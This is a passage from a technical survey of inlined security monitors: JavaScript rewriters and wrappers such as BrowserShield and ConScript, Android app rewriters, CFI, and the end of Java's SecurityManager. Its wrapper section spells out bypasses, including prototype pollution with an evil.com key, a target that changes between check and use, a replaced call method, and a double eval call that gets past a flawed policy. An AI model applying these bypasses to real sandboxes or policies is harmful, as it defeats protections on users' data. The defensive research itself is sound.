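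Finally, the system must run the checker on every program before executing it. Hamlen's rewriter and checker were separate command-line tools, and he expected difficulties in building them into .NET, which compiles each method when a program first uses it and keeps the compiled copy for later. Programs that generate code while running are harder to handle. JavaScript's `eval` function, for example, runs a string as code, and the program may build that string partly from user input. In a typical arrangement for web advertising, the publisher rewrites each advertisement and the user's computer only certifies it, so the user's computer has no rewriter to add checks to the new code.

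## Rewriting JavaScript in the browser: BrowserShield to ConScript

Scripts on web pages routinely generate more code while they run, so a rewriter can't finish before the browser opens the page. BrowserShield and CoreScript therefore keep rewriting code as the scripts run. Later systems avoid rewriting scripts, either by wrapping the browser's built-in functions or by changing its script engine.

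### Why JavaScript is harder to rewrite than Java bytecode

A script can run a string as code with `eval`, or use `document.write` to add HTML containing more scripts. *JavaScript Sandboxing* (Van Acker and Sabelfeld, 2016) gives the example of a page that asks the user for a line of text and passes it to `eval` only if its MD5 hash matches a particular value. Because MD5 is hard to reverse, a tool that inspected the page in advance could not tell what code would run.

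A Java call instruction names a class and a method, but JavaScript objects have no fixed class. A script can replace an object's methods or store a function under a new name. After `f = document.write`, for example, a call through `f` doesn't contain the name `document.write`. Reflection is also part of JavaScript's ordinary syntax, since `obj[name]` can refer to any property of an object. A JavaScript rewriter therefore has to check almost every property access, rather than putting its checks around a reflection library as a Java rewriter can. JavaScript also has nothing like Java's type safety to keep the page's scripts away from the monitor's own variables.

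Pages also mix code from several parties. A script included from another site runs with all the page's rights. Van Acker and Sabelfeld cite a 2012 study that found such scripts on 88% of the 10,000 most popular sites. In September 2014, attackers broke into the server that distributes jQuery, a library used on most large sites. They did not alter the library, but they could have changed the code that many of those sites ran.

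### How BrowserShield rewrites a page

*BrowserShield* (Reis, Dunagan and colleagues, 2006) was designed to protect Internet Explorer between the release of a security patch and its installation. Its policies are filters for known vulnerabilities. One flaw let an attacker overflow a buffer with a frame whose name and address were both too long, so the filter measures both and stops the page if they exceed the limit. Scanning the HTML at a firewall would not be enough, because a script could create the frame later.

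BrowserShield therefore translates each page in stages:

1. A firewall applies the filters to the HTML, adds a link to the BrowserShield library and wraps each script in a call to the library's translator.
2. When the browser reaches a script, the translator rewrites it so that its function calls and property accesses go through the library.
3. If the rewritten script generates HTML or code, the library translates that as well before the browser uses it.

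The rewritten code looks like this:

```
foo(x)             ->  bshield.invokeFunc(foo, x)
document.write(s)  ->  bshield.invokeMeth(document, "write", s)
obj.x = obj.y      ->  bshield.propWrite(obj, "x", bshield.propRead(obj, "y"))
```

BrowserShield needs both caller-side and callee-side checks. Scripts can't redefine some built-in functions, such as `alert`, so the library has to check calls to them at the caller. It replaces each sensitive method with a wrapper, which stays attached if a script gives the method another name. It doesn't use a central table of everything to check, because the table would keep objects in memory after the page had finished with them. Method calls need caller-side checks too, because a script can disguise a function as a method, as in `obj.m = eval`. BrowserShield doesn't have to deal with races between threads, because JavaScript is single-threaded.

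To protect the library, the translator renames any variable called `bshield` in the page's scripts to `bshield_`, and loops over an object's properties skip the library's own data. The library also keeps the original text of each script and returns it when the script reads its own code.

The firewall component has 2,679 lines of C++ and the library has 3,493 lines of JavaScript. Much of this code parses HTML and JavaScript, and it must do so exactly as the browser does. If BrowserShield and the browser identify different starting points for a script, for example, BrowserShield can miss an attack. Reis and colleagues tried to match Internet Explorer's behaviour by testing and refinement.

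### BrowserShield's coverage and costs

In 2005, Microsoft released eight critical patches for Internet Explorer, which fixed 19 vulnerabilities. Reis and colleagues judged that BrowserShield could handle all 12 that involved HTML, scripts or ActiveX components. Two of the three HTTP vulnerabilities required both BrowserShield and an HTTP filter, and antivirus software could handle the four that involved images and other files. Existing tools alone could have replaced one of the eight patches, but with BrowserShield they could have replaced all eight.

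These figures come mostly from analysing the design. The researchers tested three vulnerabilities, one from 2004, with pages that crashed an unpatched browser. BrowserShield prevented the crashes.

The slowdown depends on what a script does. The table gives running times as multiples of the original code's time.

| Operation | BrowserShield |
|---|---|
| Add two variables | 1.00 |
| Call an empty function | 44.8 |
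| Run a short assignment through `eval` | 47.3 |
| Write a property | 342 |
| Swap two images on the page | 1.07 |

Swapping the images takes two property writes, but the browser spends so long redrawing the page that the total rises only from 26.7 to 28.5 milliseconds. A script that mostly computes would slow down far more.

On average, pages took 1.7 seconds longer to appear. The ten slowest pages went from 3.9 to 10.2 seconds, and translation inside the browser accounted for 2.8 seconds of that increase. Processor use at the firewall rose from 15.0% to 18.3%.

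All these page measurements come from the 70 pages, in a sample of 250, that the prototype displayed correctly. Reis and colleagues attribute the failures to unfinished parts of the prototype, such as bugs in its JavaScript parser. BrowserShield was therefore far from transparent in practice, though better engineering might have fixed much of this. eWeek's *Microsoft Research Builds BrowserShield* described it as a prototype that Microsoft might eventually build into a product.

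### CoreScript's model of scripts that write scripts

*JavaScript Instrumentation for Browser Security* (Yu, Chander and colleagues, 2007) formalizes the same technique for CoreScript, a small subset of JavaScript. In CoreScript, running a script replaces it with the piece of document it produces, which may contain more scripts. The rewriter changes each security-relevant action *A* to `check(A)`, which consults the policy. It changes each `write(E)` to `instr(E)`, which evaluates *E* at run time and rewrites the result before the browser runs any script inside it. Policies are edit automata, and one example resembles the file-and-message policy: after a script reads a cookie, the automaton replaces each page load with a safe version that asks the user before contacting a different site. Yu and colleagues prove that the rewriting is transparent and that rewritten programs obey any policy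 that accepts its own replacement actions. But CoreScript leaves out objects, which they consider a separate matter, so the proof does not cover the aliased methods and altered properties that were so difficult for BrowserShield to handle.

### Wrapper libraries inside the page

Phung, Sands and Chudnov (2009), in *Lightweight Self-Protecting JavaScript*, enforce policies without parsing scripts or changing the browser. A small library wraps security-relevant built-in functions, and later scripts call the wrappers. Code that scripts generate at run time calls them too, so it needs no rewriting. Phung and colleagues show, in an abstract model, that the method can enforce security automata.

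This simplified wrapper lets a page send messages only to Google:

```
var original = window.postMessage;
var allowed = { "http://www.google.com": true };

window.postMessage = function (message, target) {
    if (!allowed[target]) throw "blocked";
    return original.call(this, message, target);
};
```

The untrusted script can't name `original` or `allowed` if the library keeps them in a private scope. It can still defeat the check by changing objects that the wrapper shares with the rest of the page. Meyerovich and Livshits (2010), in *CONSCRIPT*, describe several such attacks:

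- Every ordinary object inherits properties from `Object.prototype`. If a script sets `Object.prototype["http://evil.com"] = true`, the lookup in `allowed` succeeds for that address.
- The script can pass an object as the target, with its own method for converting itself to text. The method returns Google's address during the check and a different one when the browser sends the message.
- The wrapper uses the shared method `call` to run the original function. If the script has replaced `call`, its replacement receives the original function and can use it without any check.

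A script may also reach the original function through another path that the library's author didn't wrap. In *Safe Wrappers and Sane Policies for Self Protecting JavaScript*, Magazinius and Phung (2012) acknowledge that the 2009 implementation had a range of vulnerabilities and that writing policies for it was error-prone. They propose systematic ways to avoid both problems.

### ConScript: checks inside the script engine

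Meyerovich and Livshits moved the checks into the script engine of Internet Explorer 8. Their system, ConScript, lets a page supply a policy, written as JavaScript advice, for the scripts it includes. The command `around(f, check)` makes the engine run `check` whenever a script calls `f`.

The engine represents most functions as objects in memory, and ConScript adds a hidden pointer from each such object to the function's advice. Because the pointer is attached to the function rather than to a name, the check covers every alias. Browser-provided functions, such as those that change the page, have no such object in the engine, so ConScript looks them up in a table before each call. A separate command, `aroundScript`, passes the text of each new script to the policy before the engine parses it. The policy can return different text or an empty string.

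These changes took 969 lines of code. About half of them only make the new functions available to scripts.

Advice usually ends by calling the original function, which could trigger the same advice endlessly, much as a Polymer policy can trigger itself. ConScript therefore switches the advice off for one call each time the advice runs. A policy that refuses a call must switch the advice back on with `curse()`, or the next call goes unchecked. The ConScript paper's opening example, which restricts `eval` to reading data, has no `curse()`, so by the paper's own rules a script could get past the policy by calling `eval` twice. A later version in the same paper includes `curse()`.

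### ConScript's policies

Meyerovich and Livshits wrote 17 policies based on common mistakes in JavaScript programs and on earlier research. They found errors in many of the published policies they rewrote.

| Group | Policies | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Adding scripts | 5 | Run only scripts from a list of approved addresses |
| Communication | 4 | Send passwords only over secure connections |
| Changes to the page | 5 | Limit the number and size of pop-up windows |
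| Use of libraries | 3 | Report an error when a jQuery search finds nothing |

One policy prevents a script from creating links to other sites after it has read a cookie. In simplified form:

```
let cookieRead = false;

around(getField(document, "cookie"), function (get) {
    cookieRead = true;
    return get();
});

around(setField(link, "href"), function (set, address) {
    let url = toPrimitive(address);
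    if (!cookieRead || startsWith(url, "http://g.com/")) set(url);
    else { curse(); throw "blocked"; }
});
```

The policy covers only links, so a script could still send the cookie to another site inside the address of an image. The version printed in the paper also discards the first 12 characters of the address instead of comparing them, so it would refuse every new link after a cookie read, even one to the permitted site.

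Tools can generate some policies. Script#, a Microsoft tool, translates C# programs into JavaScript. JavaScript had no private methods at the time, so any script on the page could call methods that were private in the C# source. Meyerovich and Livshits generated a policy that allows a private method to run only while a public method of the same class is in progress. They applied it to 55 methods of Live Desktop, a file-sharing application, and detected no significant slowdown.

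ConScript also generated policies by observing applications. It recorded which of 15 risky functions an application such as Gmail used, then blocked the rest. The policies raised no false alarms in testing, but the paper reports no test against a real attack. An application could stop working if a user tried a legitimate feature that the recording had missed.

### Checking the policies themselves

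ConScript's policies are also written in JavaScript, so they are open to the attacks on shared objects even when every alias is covered. Meyerovich and Livshits added safer operations to the engine. `uCall` runs a function without looking up the shared method `call`, and `toPrimitive` converts a value to text once, so that the value can't change between being checked and being used. The helper `hasProp` ignores inherited properties.

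A type system then checks that policies use these operations where necessary. It gives each value one of three labels:

- `o` marks objects that belong to the policy, such as a list of approved addresses. The policy must not pass them to the page's code.
- `k` marks functions that the policy obtained before any untrusted script ran. The policy can safely call them.
- `u` marks everything that the page might control. The policy must not call these values as functions.

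In the `postMessage` example, the type checker would reject `original.call`, because the page may have replaced `call` by the time the policy uses it. Only policies have to pass the checker, so pages can use ordinary scripts. Meyerovich and Livshits don't formally prove that the type system is sound, because they thought no existing formal model of JavaScript was both realistic enough to include these attacks and simple enough to use. The type system also isn't designed to detect a missing `curse()` or an incorrect comparison of addresses.

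### ConScript's overhead compared with wrappers

Meyerovich and Livshits timed 10,000 calls to each of several functions, with advice that only passed the call on. The table gives times as multiples of the time for an unchecked call.

| Function | Wrapper | ConScript |
|---|---|---|
| Empty function in the page | 3.86 | 1.02 |
| `Math.tan(5)` | 1.37 | 1.27 |
| `eval("1")` | 1.53 | 1.36 |
| `getElementsByTagName("div")` | 5.57 | 1.20 |
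| Average of all seven tests | 3.42 | 1.24 |

On large sites such as MSN and Gmail, the policies generated by observation slowed loading by about 1% or less. Google Maps showed a 7% slowdown, but its times varied too much for this to be significant. The policies blocked functions that the sites didn't use, so the checks hardly ever ran, and almost all the overhead came from setting them up. These results are therefore weak evidence about the overhead of policies that check frequent events.

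ConScript policies also added only about 0.7 KB to a site's compressed code, while a rewriter's additions grow with the size of the program. The main obstacle was deployment, because a site could rely on a ConScript policy only if its visitors' browsers supported ConScript. BrowserShield and the wrapper libraries worked with existing browsers.

### What became of Caja, and what browsers standardised

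Google's Caja was the best-known attempt to use JavaScript rewriting in production. It let a site include untrusted code, such as a small application from another company, by translating it into a restricted form of JavaScript with run-time checks. Facebook and Microsoft developed similar systems. These tools worked in unmodified browsers, but they were large and hard to implement correctly. Meyerovich and Livshits counted over 181,000 lines in Caja's main source directory and noted that other researchers had questioned whether such systems were correct. Google archived Caja in January 2021.

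Freezing JavaScript's built-in objects before any untrusted code runs would stop a script from altering `Object.prototype` or replacing `call`, without the need to rewrite every operation. wal.sh's *JavaScript Security* demonstrates this on a few objects in a 2026 version of Node, a program that runs JavaScript outside the browser. Secure ECMAScript (SES), a hardened form of the language, freezes all built-in objects with its `lockdown` function.

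Browsers standardised simpler controls that don't require a site to write code. With Content Security Policy (CSP), a site sends a list of permitted sources along with the page, and the browser enforces it. Desmet and Nikiforakis, in *Sandboxing Javascript*, give this example:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'self'; object-src 'none'
```

A Content Security Policy (CSP) can restrict the browser to loading scripts only from the site itself and block all plug-ins. By default, such a policy also blocks `eval` and scripts written directly into the HTML. CSP covers much of what ConScript's script policies do, without advice that an attacker could subvert.

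A sandboxed frame isolates untrusted content in a separate part of the page:

```
<iframe src="https://ads.example/ad.html" sandbox="allow-scripts"></iframe>
```

Scripts in this frame can run, but the browser treats them as coming from a different site. They can't read the surrounding page or its cookies, and can communicate with the page only through messages. This suits an advertisement better than a library like jQuery, which has to work directly on the page's contents.

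All major browsers now support both mechanisms, but neither can express the cookie policy above, because their restrictions don't depend on what a script has already read. A site can use CSP to restrict where its pages send data, for example, but the restriction applies whether or not a script has read a cookie. *WebPol* (2017), a paper on information-flow policies for browsers, calls such mechanisms too coarse for third-party scripts. They control whether a script can access data, but a site often needs to let a script use confidential data without leaking it.

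## Rewriting Android apps to restrict their permissions

Android's original permission system was also too coarse for many purposes. Before Android 6, users had to accept every permission an app listed at installation or do without the app, and they could not withdraw a permission later (Backes, Gerling and colleagues, 2012, *AppGuard*). Many permissions covered more than the app needed. Amazon's shopping app, for example, needed the Internet permission to reach Amazon's servers, but could then exchange data with any site (Jeon, Micinski and colleagues, 2012, *Dr. Android and Mr. Hide*).

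Researchers had proposed finer controls, but most required a modified version of Android. Installing one could void a phone's warranty, and every manufacturer had its own variant of the system. Apps are easier to modify because each arrives as a single file that a tool can rewrite before the user installs the app. This file, called an Android package or APK, contains the app's bytecode, its resources and a manifest that lists its permissions.

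### Where three systems put their checks

To send a text message, an app calls a Java method in Android's framework library, which runs inside the app's process. The library passes the request through native code and the C library to the kernel, which delivers it to a system service in another process. The service checks that the app has the required permission and then sends the message. A monitor can intercept the request at several points along this path.

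Aurasium (Xu, Saïdi and Anderson, 2012) intercepts an app's calls at the C library. Each native library in the process has a table of the addresses of outside functions that it calls, and Aurasium replaces some of these addresses with those of its own functions. Whichever Java networking class an app uses, for example, the request goes through the C library's `connect` function, so one check covers them all. This avoids the long lists of Java methods that made earlier policies hard to write.

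Requests for text messages, contacts and the phone's location all pass through a single function, `ioctl`, as blocks of bytes. Aurasium has to reconstruct the original request from these bytes before it can apply a policy. Xu and colleagues found that the format had barely changed between Android 2.2 and 3.x, but Google could change it in any later version.

Dr. Android and Mr. Hide are two parts of one system. Dr. Android rewrites an app, replacing a broad permission in its manifest with a narrower one and redirecting the relevant calls to a replacement library. The library forwards each request to Mr. Hide, a group of services that run in separate processes and hold the original Android permissions. Mr. Hide checks the app's narrower permission before performing the operation. It can restrict an app to particular Internet domains, particular fields of the user's contacts or a location accurate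 to about 150 metres.

AppGuard intercepts calls to Java methods. Its first public release inserted checks before calls in the app's bytecode. The 2013 report *AppGuard* (Backes, Gerling and colleagues) describes a later version, which changes the virtual machine's references to methods inside the running app so that calls to restricted methods go to the monitor. This also catches calls made through reflection, calls from code that the app loads later, and calls from native code to Java methods.

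| | Aurasium | Dr. Android and Mr. Hide | AppGuard (2013) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code added to the app | A native library and policy code in Java | A library that forwards requests | A monitor and its policy settings |
| What the system changes | Addresses of C library functions | Permissions in the manifest and class names in the bytecode | References to Java methods |
| What the check can examine | Low-level arguments, from which it rebuilds the request | The forwarded request and the app's permissions | Java arguments and objects |
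| What it can't control | Native code that bypasses the C library | How the app uses data it has received | System calls from native code |

Working with Java objects lets AppGuard enforce some policies that Aurasium can't. One of them replaces the insecure hash function MD5 with SHA-1. MD5 is pure computation, so it makes no distinctive C library call for Aurasium to intercept.

Of the three systems, Mr. Hide handles gaps in its coverage most safely. Dr. Android removes the app's Internet permission, so if the replacement library lacks a method for opening Internet connections, an app that uses the method can't connect, and the user notices a broken feature. In the other two systems, the app keeps its original permissions, so any call they miss succeeds without a check.

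Backes and colleagues object that an external monitor must hold the permissions of every app it monitors. Jeon and colleagues reduce this risk by giving each Mr. Hide service only one Android permission. A harder objection to answer is that if a policy depends on the app's internal state, the app must send that state to the monitor, which takes time.

### Policies on secret data

Aurasium's policies mostly concern single events. If an app tries to send a text message to a premium number, Aurasium shows the user the number and the text and asks for approval. If the user refuses an app's request for private data, Aurasium gives the app made-up data. Xu and colleagues planned to add policies on sequences of events, written as automata.

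AppGuard's 2013 policy language already had automata. It extended SPoX with rules that replace one method call with another and rules that mark a method's result as secret. The monitor keeps the secret value and gives the app only a handle, which the app can use in operations the policy allows.

One example is for messaging apps that need to find out which of a user's contacts have accounts. In simplified form, the policy treats the app's calls as follows:

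```
list   = query(contacts, phone numbers)   -> secret
more   = list.moveToNext()                -> public
number = list.getString(...)              -> secret
bytes  = number.getBytes()                -> secret
code   = hash(bytes)                      -> public
```

The app can send the hash to its server but never receives the number itself. This protection is limited because phone numbers are short, so a server could hash every possible number and look for a match. The app can also count the contacts, because it can see from `moveToNext` whether there is another entry.

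### How well the rewritten apps worked

All three systems slowed the calls they monitored, but few rewritten apps failed completely. The slowdowns in the table come from small tests that mostly repeat one kind of call, and the phones and operations differed between tests, so the figures can't be used to rank the systems.

| | Aurasium | Dr. Android and Mr. Hide | AppGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| Apps in the test | 4,751 | 14 | 25,000 |
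| Result | Rewrote 99.6%; all 3,189 that the researchers ran started | All ran, but seven lost web content or advertisements | The "vast majority" still worked |
| Added size | 52 KB on average | Not reported | 41 to 48 KB in seven apps |
| Slowdown of monitored calls | 14% to 35% | 10% to 50% | 1% to 21% |

The results for Aurasium and Dr. Android come from very different tests. Xu and colleagues took 3,491 apps from an app store and 1,260 malware samples. They ran each store app with a program that generated 500 random clicks and other events. Every app started, and Aurasium intercepted the first monitored call in each. But fewer than half of the apps with the Internet permission used it during the tests, so many features probably never ran.

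Jeon and colleagues instead tried almost every feature of their 14 apps by hand, before and after rewriting. They had chosen apps that suited their tools, so the sample can't show how often Dr. Android would succeed on an arbitrary app. The seven partial failures all occurred because Mr. Hide didn't support WebView, which displays web pages inside an app and which many apps also used for advertisements. The rewritten apps showed placeholder text in place of WebView content.

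Their study also tested whether narrower permissions would suit real apps. In the 14 apps, they judged that finer permissions could replace 31 of 35 uses of the broad permissions they studied, with little loss to the user. A static analysis of 750 popular apps found a median of eight Internet domains mentioned in each app. That list is short enough for a user to read, but a file manager that connects to any server the user chooses would still need full Internet access.

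Aurasium's 14% slowdown for 200 contact queries is probably too high, since the queries took 1,270 milliseconds before rewriting and 1,340 afterwards, an increase of about 6%. The 35% slowdown is for requests for device information. Two ordinary benchmark apps, which make few such requests, ran at almost the same speed as before.

Mr. Hide's overhead comes from communication between processes. Fetching 100 web pages took 25% longer and 100 contact queries took 50% longer. Jeon and colleagues noticed a delay when some apps started and connected to the services, but little difference after that.

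The size figures for AppGuard come from its first release, which Backes, Gerling and colleagues describe in a conference paper of the same name. Rewriting took 4.5 to 47 seconds on the phone itself, with Facebook's app the slowest. In tests of three monitored methods, calls took 1.0% to 6.2% longer with the inserted code.

AppGuard also stopped some real leaks. Twitter's app had been uploading users' address books without consent. When Backes and colleagues blocked its access to contacts, the app lost only its friend-finding feature. They also let a weather app connect only to its own company's servers, which kept the forecasts but removed the advertisements. Users might like that, but the developer loses income.

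AppGuard was the most widely distributed of the three. The conference paper reports more than 500,000 downloads, and the later 2013 report about 1,000,000, but neither figure measures how many people kept using it.

### Signatures and updates

Android requires every app to have a valid digital signature, and any change to the package invalidates it. A rewriter doesn't have the developer's private key, so it has to sign the modified app with its own key. Android allows this because it doesn't require an outside authority to approve the key. But Android uses signatures to recognise apps by the same developer, which can share data with one another, and to confirm that an update comes from the developer of the installed app.

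Aurasium and AppGuard sign all of a developer's rewritten apps with the same replacement key, so those apps can still share data with each other. If the user rewrites only one of two such apps, their signatures no longer match and they can't share data. Aurasium has to store the replacement keys securely, because anyone who stole one could sign a malicious update that Android would accept for a rewritten app.

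Updates are a greater problem. Google Play delivers updates signed with the developer's key, but the installed app is signed with the replacement key, so Android rejects them. Somebody has to obtain each new version, rewrite it and sign it with the replacement key. Until then, the user keeps the old version, including any security flaws that the developer has since fixed.

Xu and colleagues considered this a minor problem because they expected people to use Aurasium mainly on standalone apps from untrusted sources. The argument doesn't apply to AppGuard, whose users might rewrite popular apps like Facebook's and Twitter's. AppGuard's first release prevented rewritten apps from updating through Google Play. A later version updates them on the phone and keeps their data.

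Installation was inconvenient too. An Android app can't silently replace another app, so AppGuard reads the installed package, creates a modified copy and prompts the user to uninstall the original and install the copy. An app can also check its own signature and exit if the signature has changed, which legitimate developers do to detect copies altered by criminals. Aurasium could return the original signature when the app checks, but Xu and colleagues expected a determined developer to find a way around this.

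### Sharing a process with the app

Aurasium and AppGuard run in the same process as the app they monitor. Aurasium has to stop the app's Java code from using reflection to change the monitor's data and from opening the file that stores the user's decisions. Native code is more dangerous, as it is for any bytecode monitor, because it can restore the original addresses in the tables or make system calls directly.

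Aurasium starts before the app's own code, so it can detect the first attempt to load a native library. It then prompts the user to allow or refuse the load, with a warning that the library could disable the monitor. This is a poor choice to offer, because refusing will usually crash the app and most users can't judge whether the library is safe. Xu and colleagues found native libraries in 226 of roughly 3,000 apps. They proposed confining such code with techniques similar to software fault isolation but had not implemented this.

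Mr. Hide is safer in this respect, because native code in the app can't reach the monitor's memory or use a permission that the app no longer has.

### Moving AppGuard's decisions into Android

Backes, Bugiel and colleagues (2014), in *Android Security Framework*, tried a compromise between inlining and an external monitor. Their framework is a modified version of Android 4.3 to which developers can add access-control systems as modules. They divided AppGuard into three parts:

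- Hooks inside the app intercept Java methods and carry out the decisions.
- A module in the operating system stores the settings and decides whether to allow each call.
- A separate app lets the user change the settings and read the log.

The code inside the app is 4,277 lines long, and the module is 782. Adapting AppGuard mostly involved moving the decisions out, which changed 728 lines. Connecting the existing hooks to the framework changed 46. The new version made the same decisions as the original on AppGuard's own policies.

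Hooks inside the app can use information that a system service doesn't have. For example, a hook can examine the call stack to tell whether a request came from the app's main code or from an advertising library. The framework adds the hooks to the app's memory each time the app starts, so the package and its signature stay intact and ordinary updates should work.

The app can't change the settings in the operating system's module, but it could still remove a hook, and then the module would never receive the request. Backes and colleagues acknowledge that there is no strong security boundary between the hooks and the app. The new design also requires a modified operating system, which AppGuard originally avoided.

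### After Android 6

Android 6, which Google released in 2015, lets users grant access to sensitive data such as contacts and location while an app is running, and withdraw it later. This covers AppGuard's simplest use without breaking apps' signatures or updates. Many phones were slow to receive Android 6. *RmPerm a Tool for Android Permissions Removal* cites 2017 figures in which earlier versions still accounted for 71.5% of Android use.

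The new permissions removed much of the reason to rewrite apps, but they couldn't enforce every policy that rewriting could. Android 6 grants the Internet permission automatically, so a user can't limit a shopping app to the shop's own servers, which Mr. Hide made possible. Android 6 also has no equivalent of AppGuard's rule that replaces unencrypted web connections with encrypted ones.

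## Why few inlined monitors reached production

Most monitors with user-written policies never left research, with AppGuard and Caja the main exceptions. Inlined checks with one fixed policy spread much further. Becker, Hollick and Classen (2024), in *SoK*, found that all the most common operating systems supported one such check, control-flow integrity. A good explanation of why monitors with user-written policies failed must also account for the spread of fixed-policy checks.

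### Fixed policies that shipped

Native Client was Google's system for running compiled C and C++ programs in the Chrome browser. It used software fault isolation to keep each program in its own memory region, and it banned system calls and other unsafe instructions. Shmatikov gives the code that Native Client required for every jump to an address computed at run time:

```
and  %eax, 0xffffffe0    ; clear the last five bits: 0x1037 becomes 0x1020
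jmp  *%eax               ; jump to the resulting address
```

Every such jump landed on a multiple of 32. The developer's compiler arranged the program so that no instruction crossed a 32-byte boundary and the two instructions above stayed in the same 32-byte block. A program therefore couldn't jump into the middle of an instruction or skip the `and`. The browser verified the layout before running the program, so it didn't have to trust the compiler.

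In 2013 Google introduced PNaCl, a portable version of Native Client. The Chromium Blog's *Goodbye PNaCl, Hello WebAssembly!* (2017) explains that PNaCl had not worked seamlessly across browsers and that few people used it. Chromium's developers moved their efforts to WebAssembly, which other browsers also supported. Google deprecated the rest of Native Client in 2020 and set its end of life on ChromeOS at version 138, according to Chrome for Developers' *Native Client*. WebAssembly runtimes still enforce the fixed policy of confining each program to its own memory.

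Control-flow integrity (CFI) protects a program from attackers who exploit its bugs. *Twenty years later* (Houy and Bartel, 2024) gives the example of a program that stores a password next to the address of a function it will call later. A password that is too long overwrites the address, so an attacker can make the program call something else. With CFI, the compiler works out which functions the call may reach and inserts a check before the call. If the address isn't that of an allowed function, the program crashes.

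Abadi, Budiu, Erlingsson and Ligatti introduced CFI in 2005. Erlingsson had co-designed SASI and PoET, and Ligatti had co-designed Polymer, so two people who worked on general policy languages also helped create the fixed policy that spread. The 2005 version rewrote already compiled programs, but every scheme that Becker and colleagues found in use relies on a compiler. According to Houy and Bartel, CFI reached the production compilers GCC and LLVM in 2014.

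Coverage still varies greatly:

| System | Files with CFI | Study |
|---|---|---|
| Windows | About 97% | Becker and colleagues |
| Google's Android 13 | 28.7% | Houy and Bartel |
| Recent Android firmware from several vendors | Under 17% | Becker and colleagues |
| Ubuntu and Debian | Under 1% | Houy and Bartel |

The two studies count files differently, so small differences between their figures mean little. On Android, Houy and Bartel found that coverage was rising, while Becker and colleagues found that it had stagnated.

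### The end of the Java SecurityManager

Few users enforced their own policies with Java's SecurityManager, even though it didn't require rewriting programs. The checks were already in Java's libraries, so a user only had to supply a policy and switch them on.

In Java 17 (2021), OpenJDK, the project that develops Java, deprecated the SecurityManager for removal. Mullan (2024) announced in *Integrated* on 12 November 2024 that the change permanently disabling it had entered Java's source code. The change took effect in Java 24, released in March 2025.

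OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021) gives most of the reasons, and Mullan and Buckley (2024), in *JEP 486*, add figures for the maintenance work. Some of these reasons apply to inlined policies too:

| Reason for removal | Does it apply to inlined policies? |
|---|---|
| Java no longer runs applets, the main untrusted code that the SecurityManager confined | Yes, for policies on downloaded programs, but servers still load plug-ins from other developers |
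| It could not address 19 of the 25 most dangerous software weaknesses on a 2020 industry list | Largely, because a monitor that controls access to files and networks does not detect malformed data |
| A developer who wanted one restriction had to grant permission for everything else the program did | No, because an inlined policy can cover one kind of action and ignore the rest |
| Applications needed the permissions of the libraries they called, unless the library's author took special care | Only if the policy reproduces stack inspection |
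| The checks were often too slow | It depends on how often the program performs the actions that the policy covers |
| Over 1,000 library methods had to check permissions, and over 1,200 had to raise their own privileges | Library authors avoid this work, but somebody must keep the policy's list of methods up to date |

The third reason made even simple policies difficult. Suppose a developer wanted a program to read files from only one directory. The program probably also wrote files or used the network, and the SecurityManager would refuse those actions unless the developer had listed them too. The developer could not allow everything except other file reads. Mullan and Buckley report that most of the few applications that enabled the SecurityManager granted all permissions to their code.

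Microsoft also abandoned code access security, the corresponding mechanism in .NET. OpenJDK cites this as a sign that permission-based decisions were falling out of favour across the industry. It doesn't give Microsoft's reasons, so the .NET case is another example of abandonment but doesn't favour a particular explanation.

Firmstone opposed the decision about Java in *Why JEP 411 Will Have a Negative Impact on Java Security*, defending the principle of least privilege, under which code gets only the permissions it needs. OpenJDK recommends containers and operating-system controls instead of the Security Manager. When a Java user objected that relying on the operating system would tie his application to one platform, Bateman (2024), in *New candidate JEP*, pointed him to a Java agent.

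A Java agent is a program that can change the bytecode of an application's classes as they load. Mullan and Buckley print an example that stops an application from shutting down the virtual machine. It replaces each call to `System.exit` with an instruction that throws an exception:

```
System.exit(1)  ->  throw new RuntimeException("System.exit not allowed")
```

This is a small inlined monitor with caller-side checks and the usual gaps. A program can still shut down the JVM by calling `Runtime.exit` or by calling `System.exit` through reflection, because the example rewrites neither call. Mullan and Buckley say malicious code has "innumerable ways" around interception, and they don't present it as a defence against such code. They considered building interception into Java but found the possible uses too varied to justify maintaining it.

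### Monitors that replaced the SecurityManager

The removal led to two production systems that are counterexamples to the idea that user-written inlined policies are impractical. OpenSearch, a search engine that loads plug-ins into its own process, had relied on the SecurityManager to confine them. Its developers began discussing a replacement in December 2021. They considered moving plug-ins to separate processes, changing the virtual machine, or dropping the protection.

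OpenSearch replaced the SecurityManager with two mechanisms. Operating-system controls restrict the whole OpenSearch process, but they can't give one plug-in fewer rights than another. A Java agent therefore inserts checks on file operations and network connections. Each check examines the call stack to identify the plug-in that made the request, then consults that plug-in's policy file. The files keep the format that OpenSearch used with the SecurityManager, so plug-in authors had little new work to do.

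The agent covers less than the SecurityManager did and doesn't check reflection, for example. OpenSearch's developers limited it to files and networks because checking everything would have slowed the program significantly and required a lot of repetitive code.

Elasticsearch, another search engine, has a similar system called Entitlements. As Elastic's *Creating classic plugins* explains, a plug-in can call restricted Java methods only if its policy file grants the matching entitlement. A policy for a plug-in that connects to an outside service might look like this:

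```
com.example.api.client:
  - outbound_network
  - set_https_connection_properties
```

The administrator sees a warning about any extra entitlements when installing the plug-in. Elastic's API index lists an `InstrumentationRegistry` with a method for checks, which suggests that Elasticsearch also inserts its checks by modifying code. One entitlement lets a plug-in load native libraries, and Elastic warns that native code may bypass the other restrictions.

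Runtime application self-protection (RASP) products use inlining to defend web applications. A company attaches the product to its own application, often as a Java agent, and the product checks operations such as database queries for signs of an attack. Companies can also use AspectJ to weave access checks into their own code. Both are evidence that inlining has commercial uses, but it is uncertain how many companies rely on them.

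### Run-time cost and gaps in coverage

Slowness has clearly limited the use of some monitors. SASI's x86 prototype slowed programs considerably even before it enforced any user policy, and OpenJDK says the SecurityManager was off by default because its checks were slow. Houy and Bartel report that most early CFI implementations had too much overhead for practical use. LLVM's x86-64 version of a CFI scheme that protects return addresses had a race between threads, and LLVM dropped it because fixing the race would have made programs unacceptably slow.

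But many monitors on method calls were fast enough and still had few users. For example, SPoX's overhead for method-call policies was too small to measure. CFI covers far more of Android than of Debian, although both can use the same compiler. Run-time overhead can therefore explain why designers avoid policies on very frequent events, but not why so few people used the faster monitors.

Gaps in coverage explain even less, since CFI spread despite large ones. Vendors evidently accept a defence that makes attacks harder without ruling them out. Every Android program that Becker and colleagues examined depended on at least one unprotected library. Under the Android scheme, a call into such a library always passes the check, even if an attacker has changed its destination. Microsoft's Control Flow Guard lets an indirect call reach any function on a single list of valid targets.

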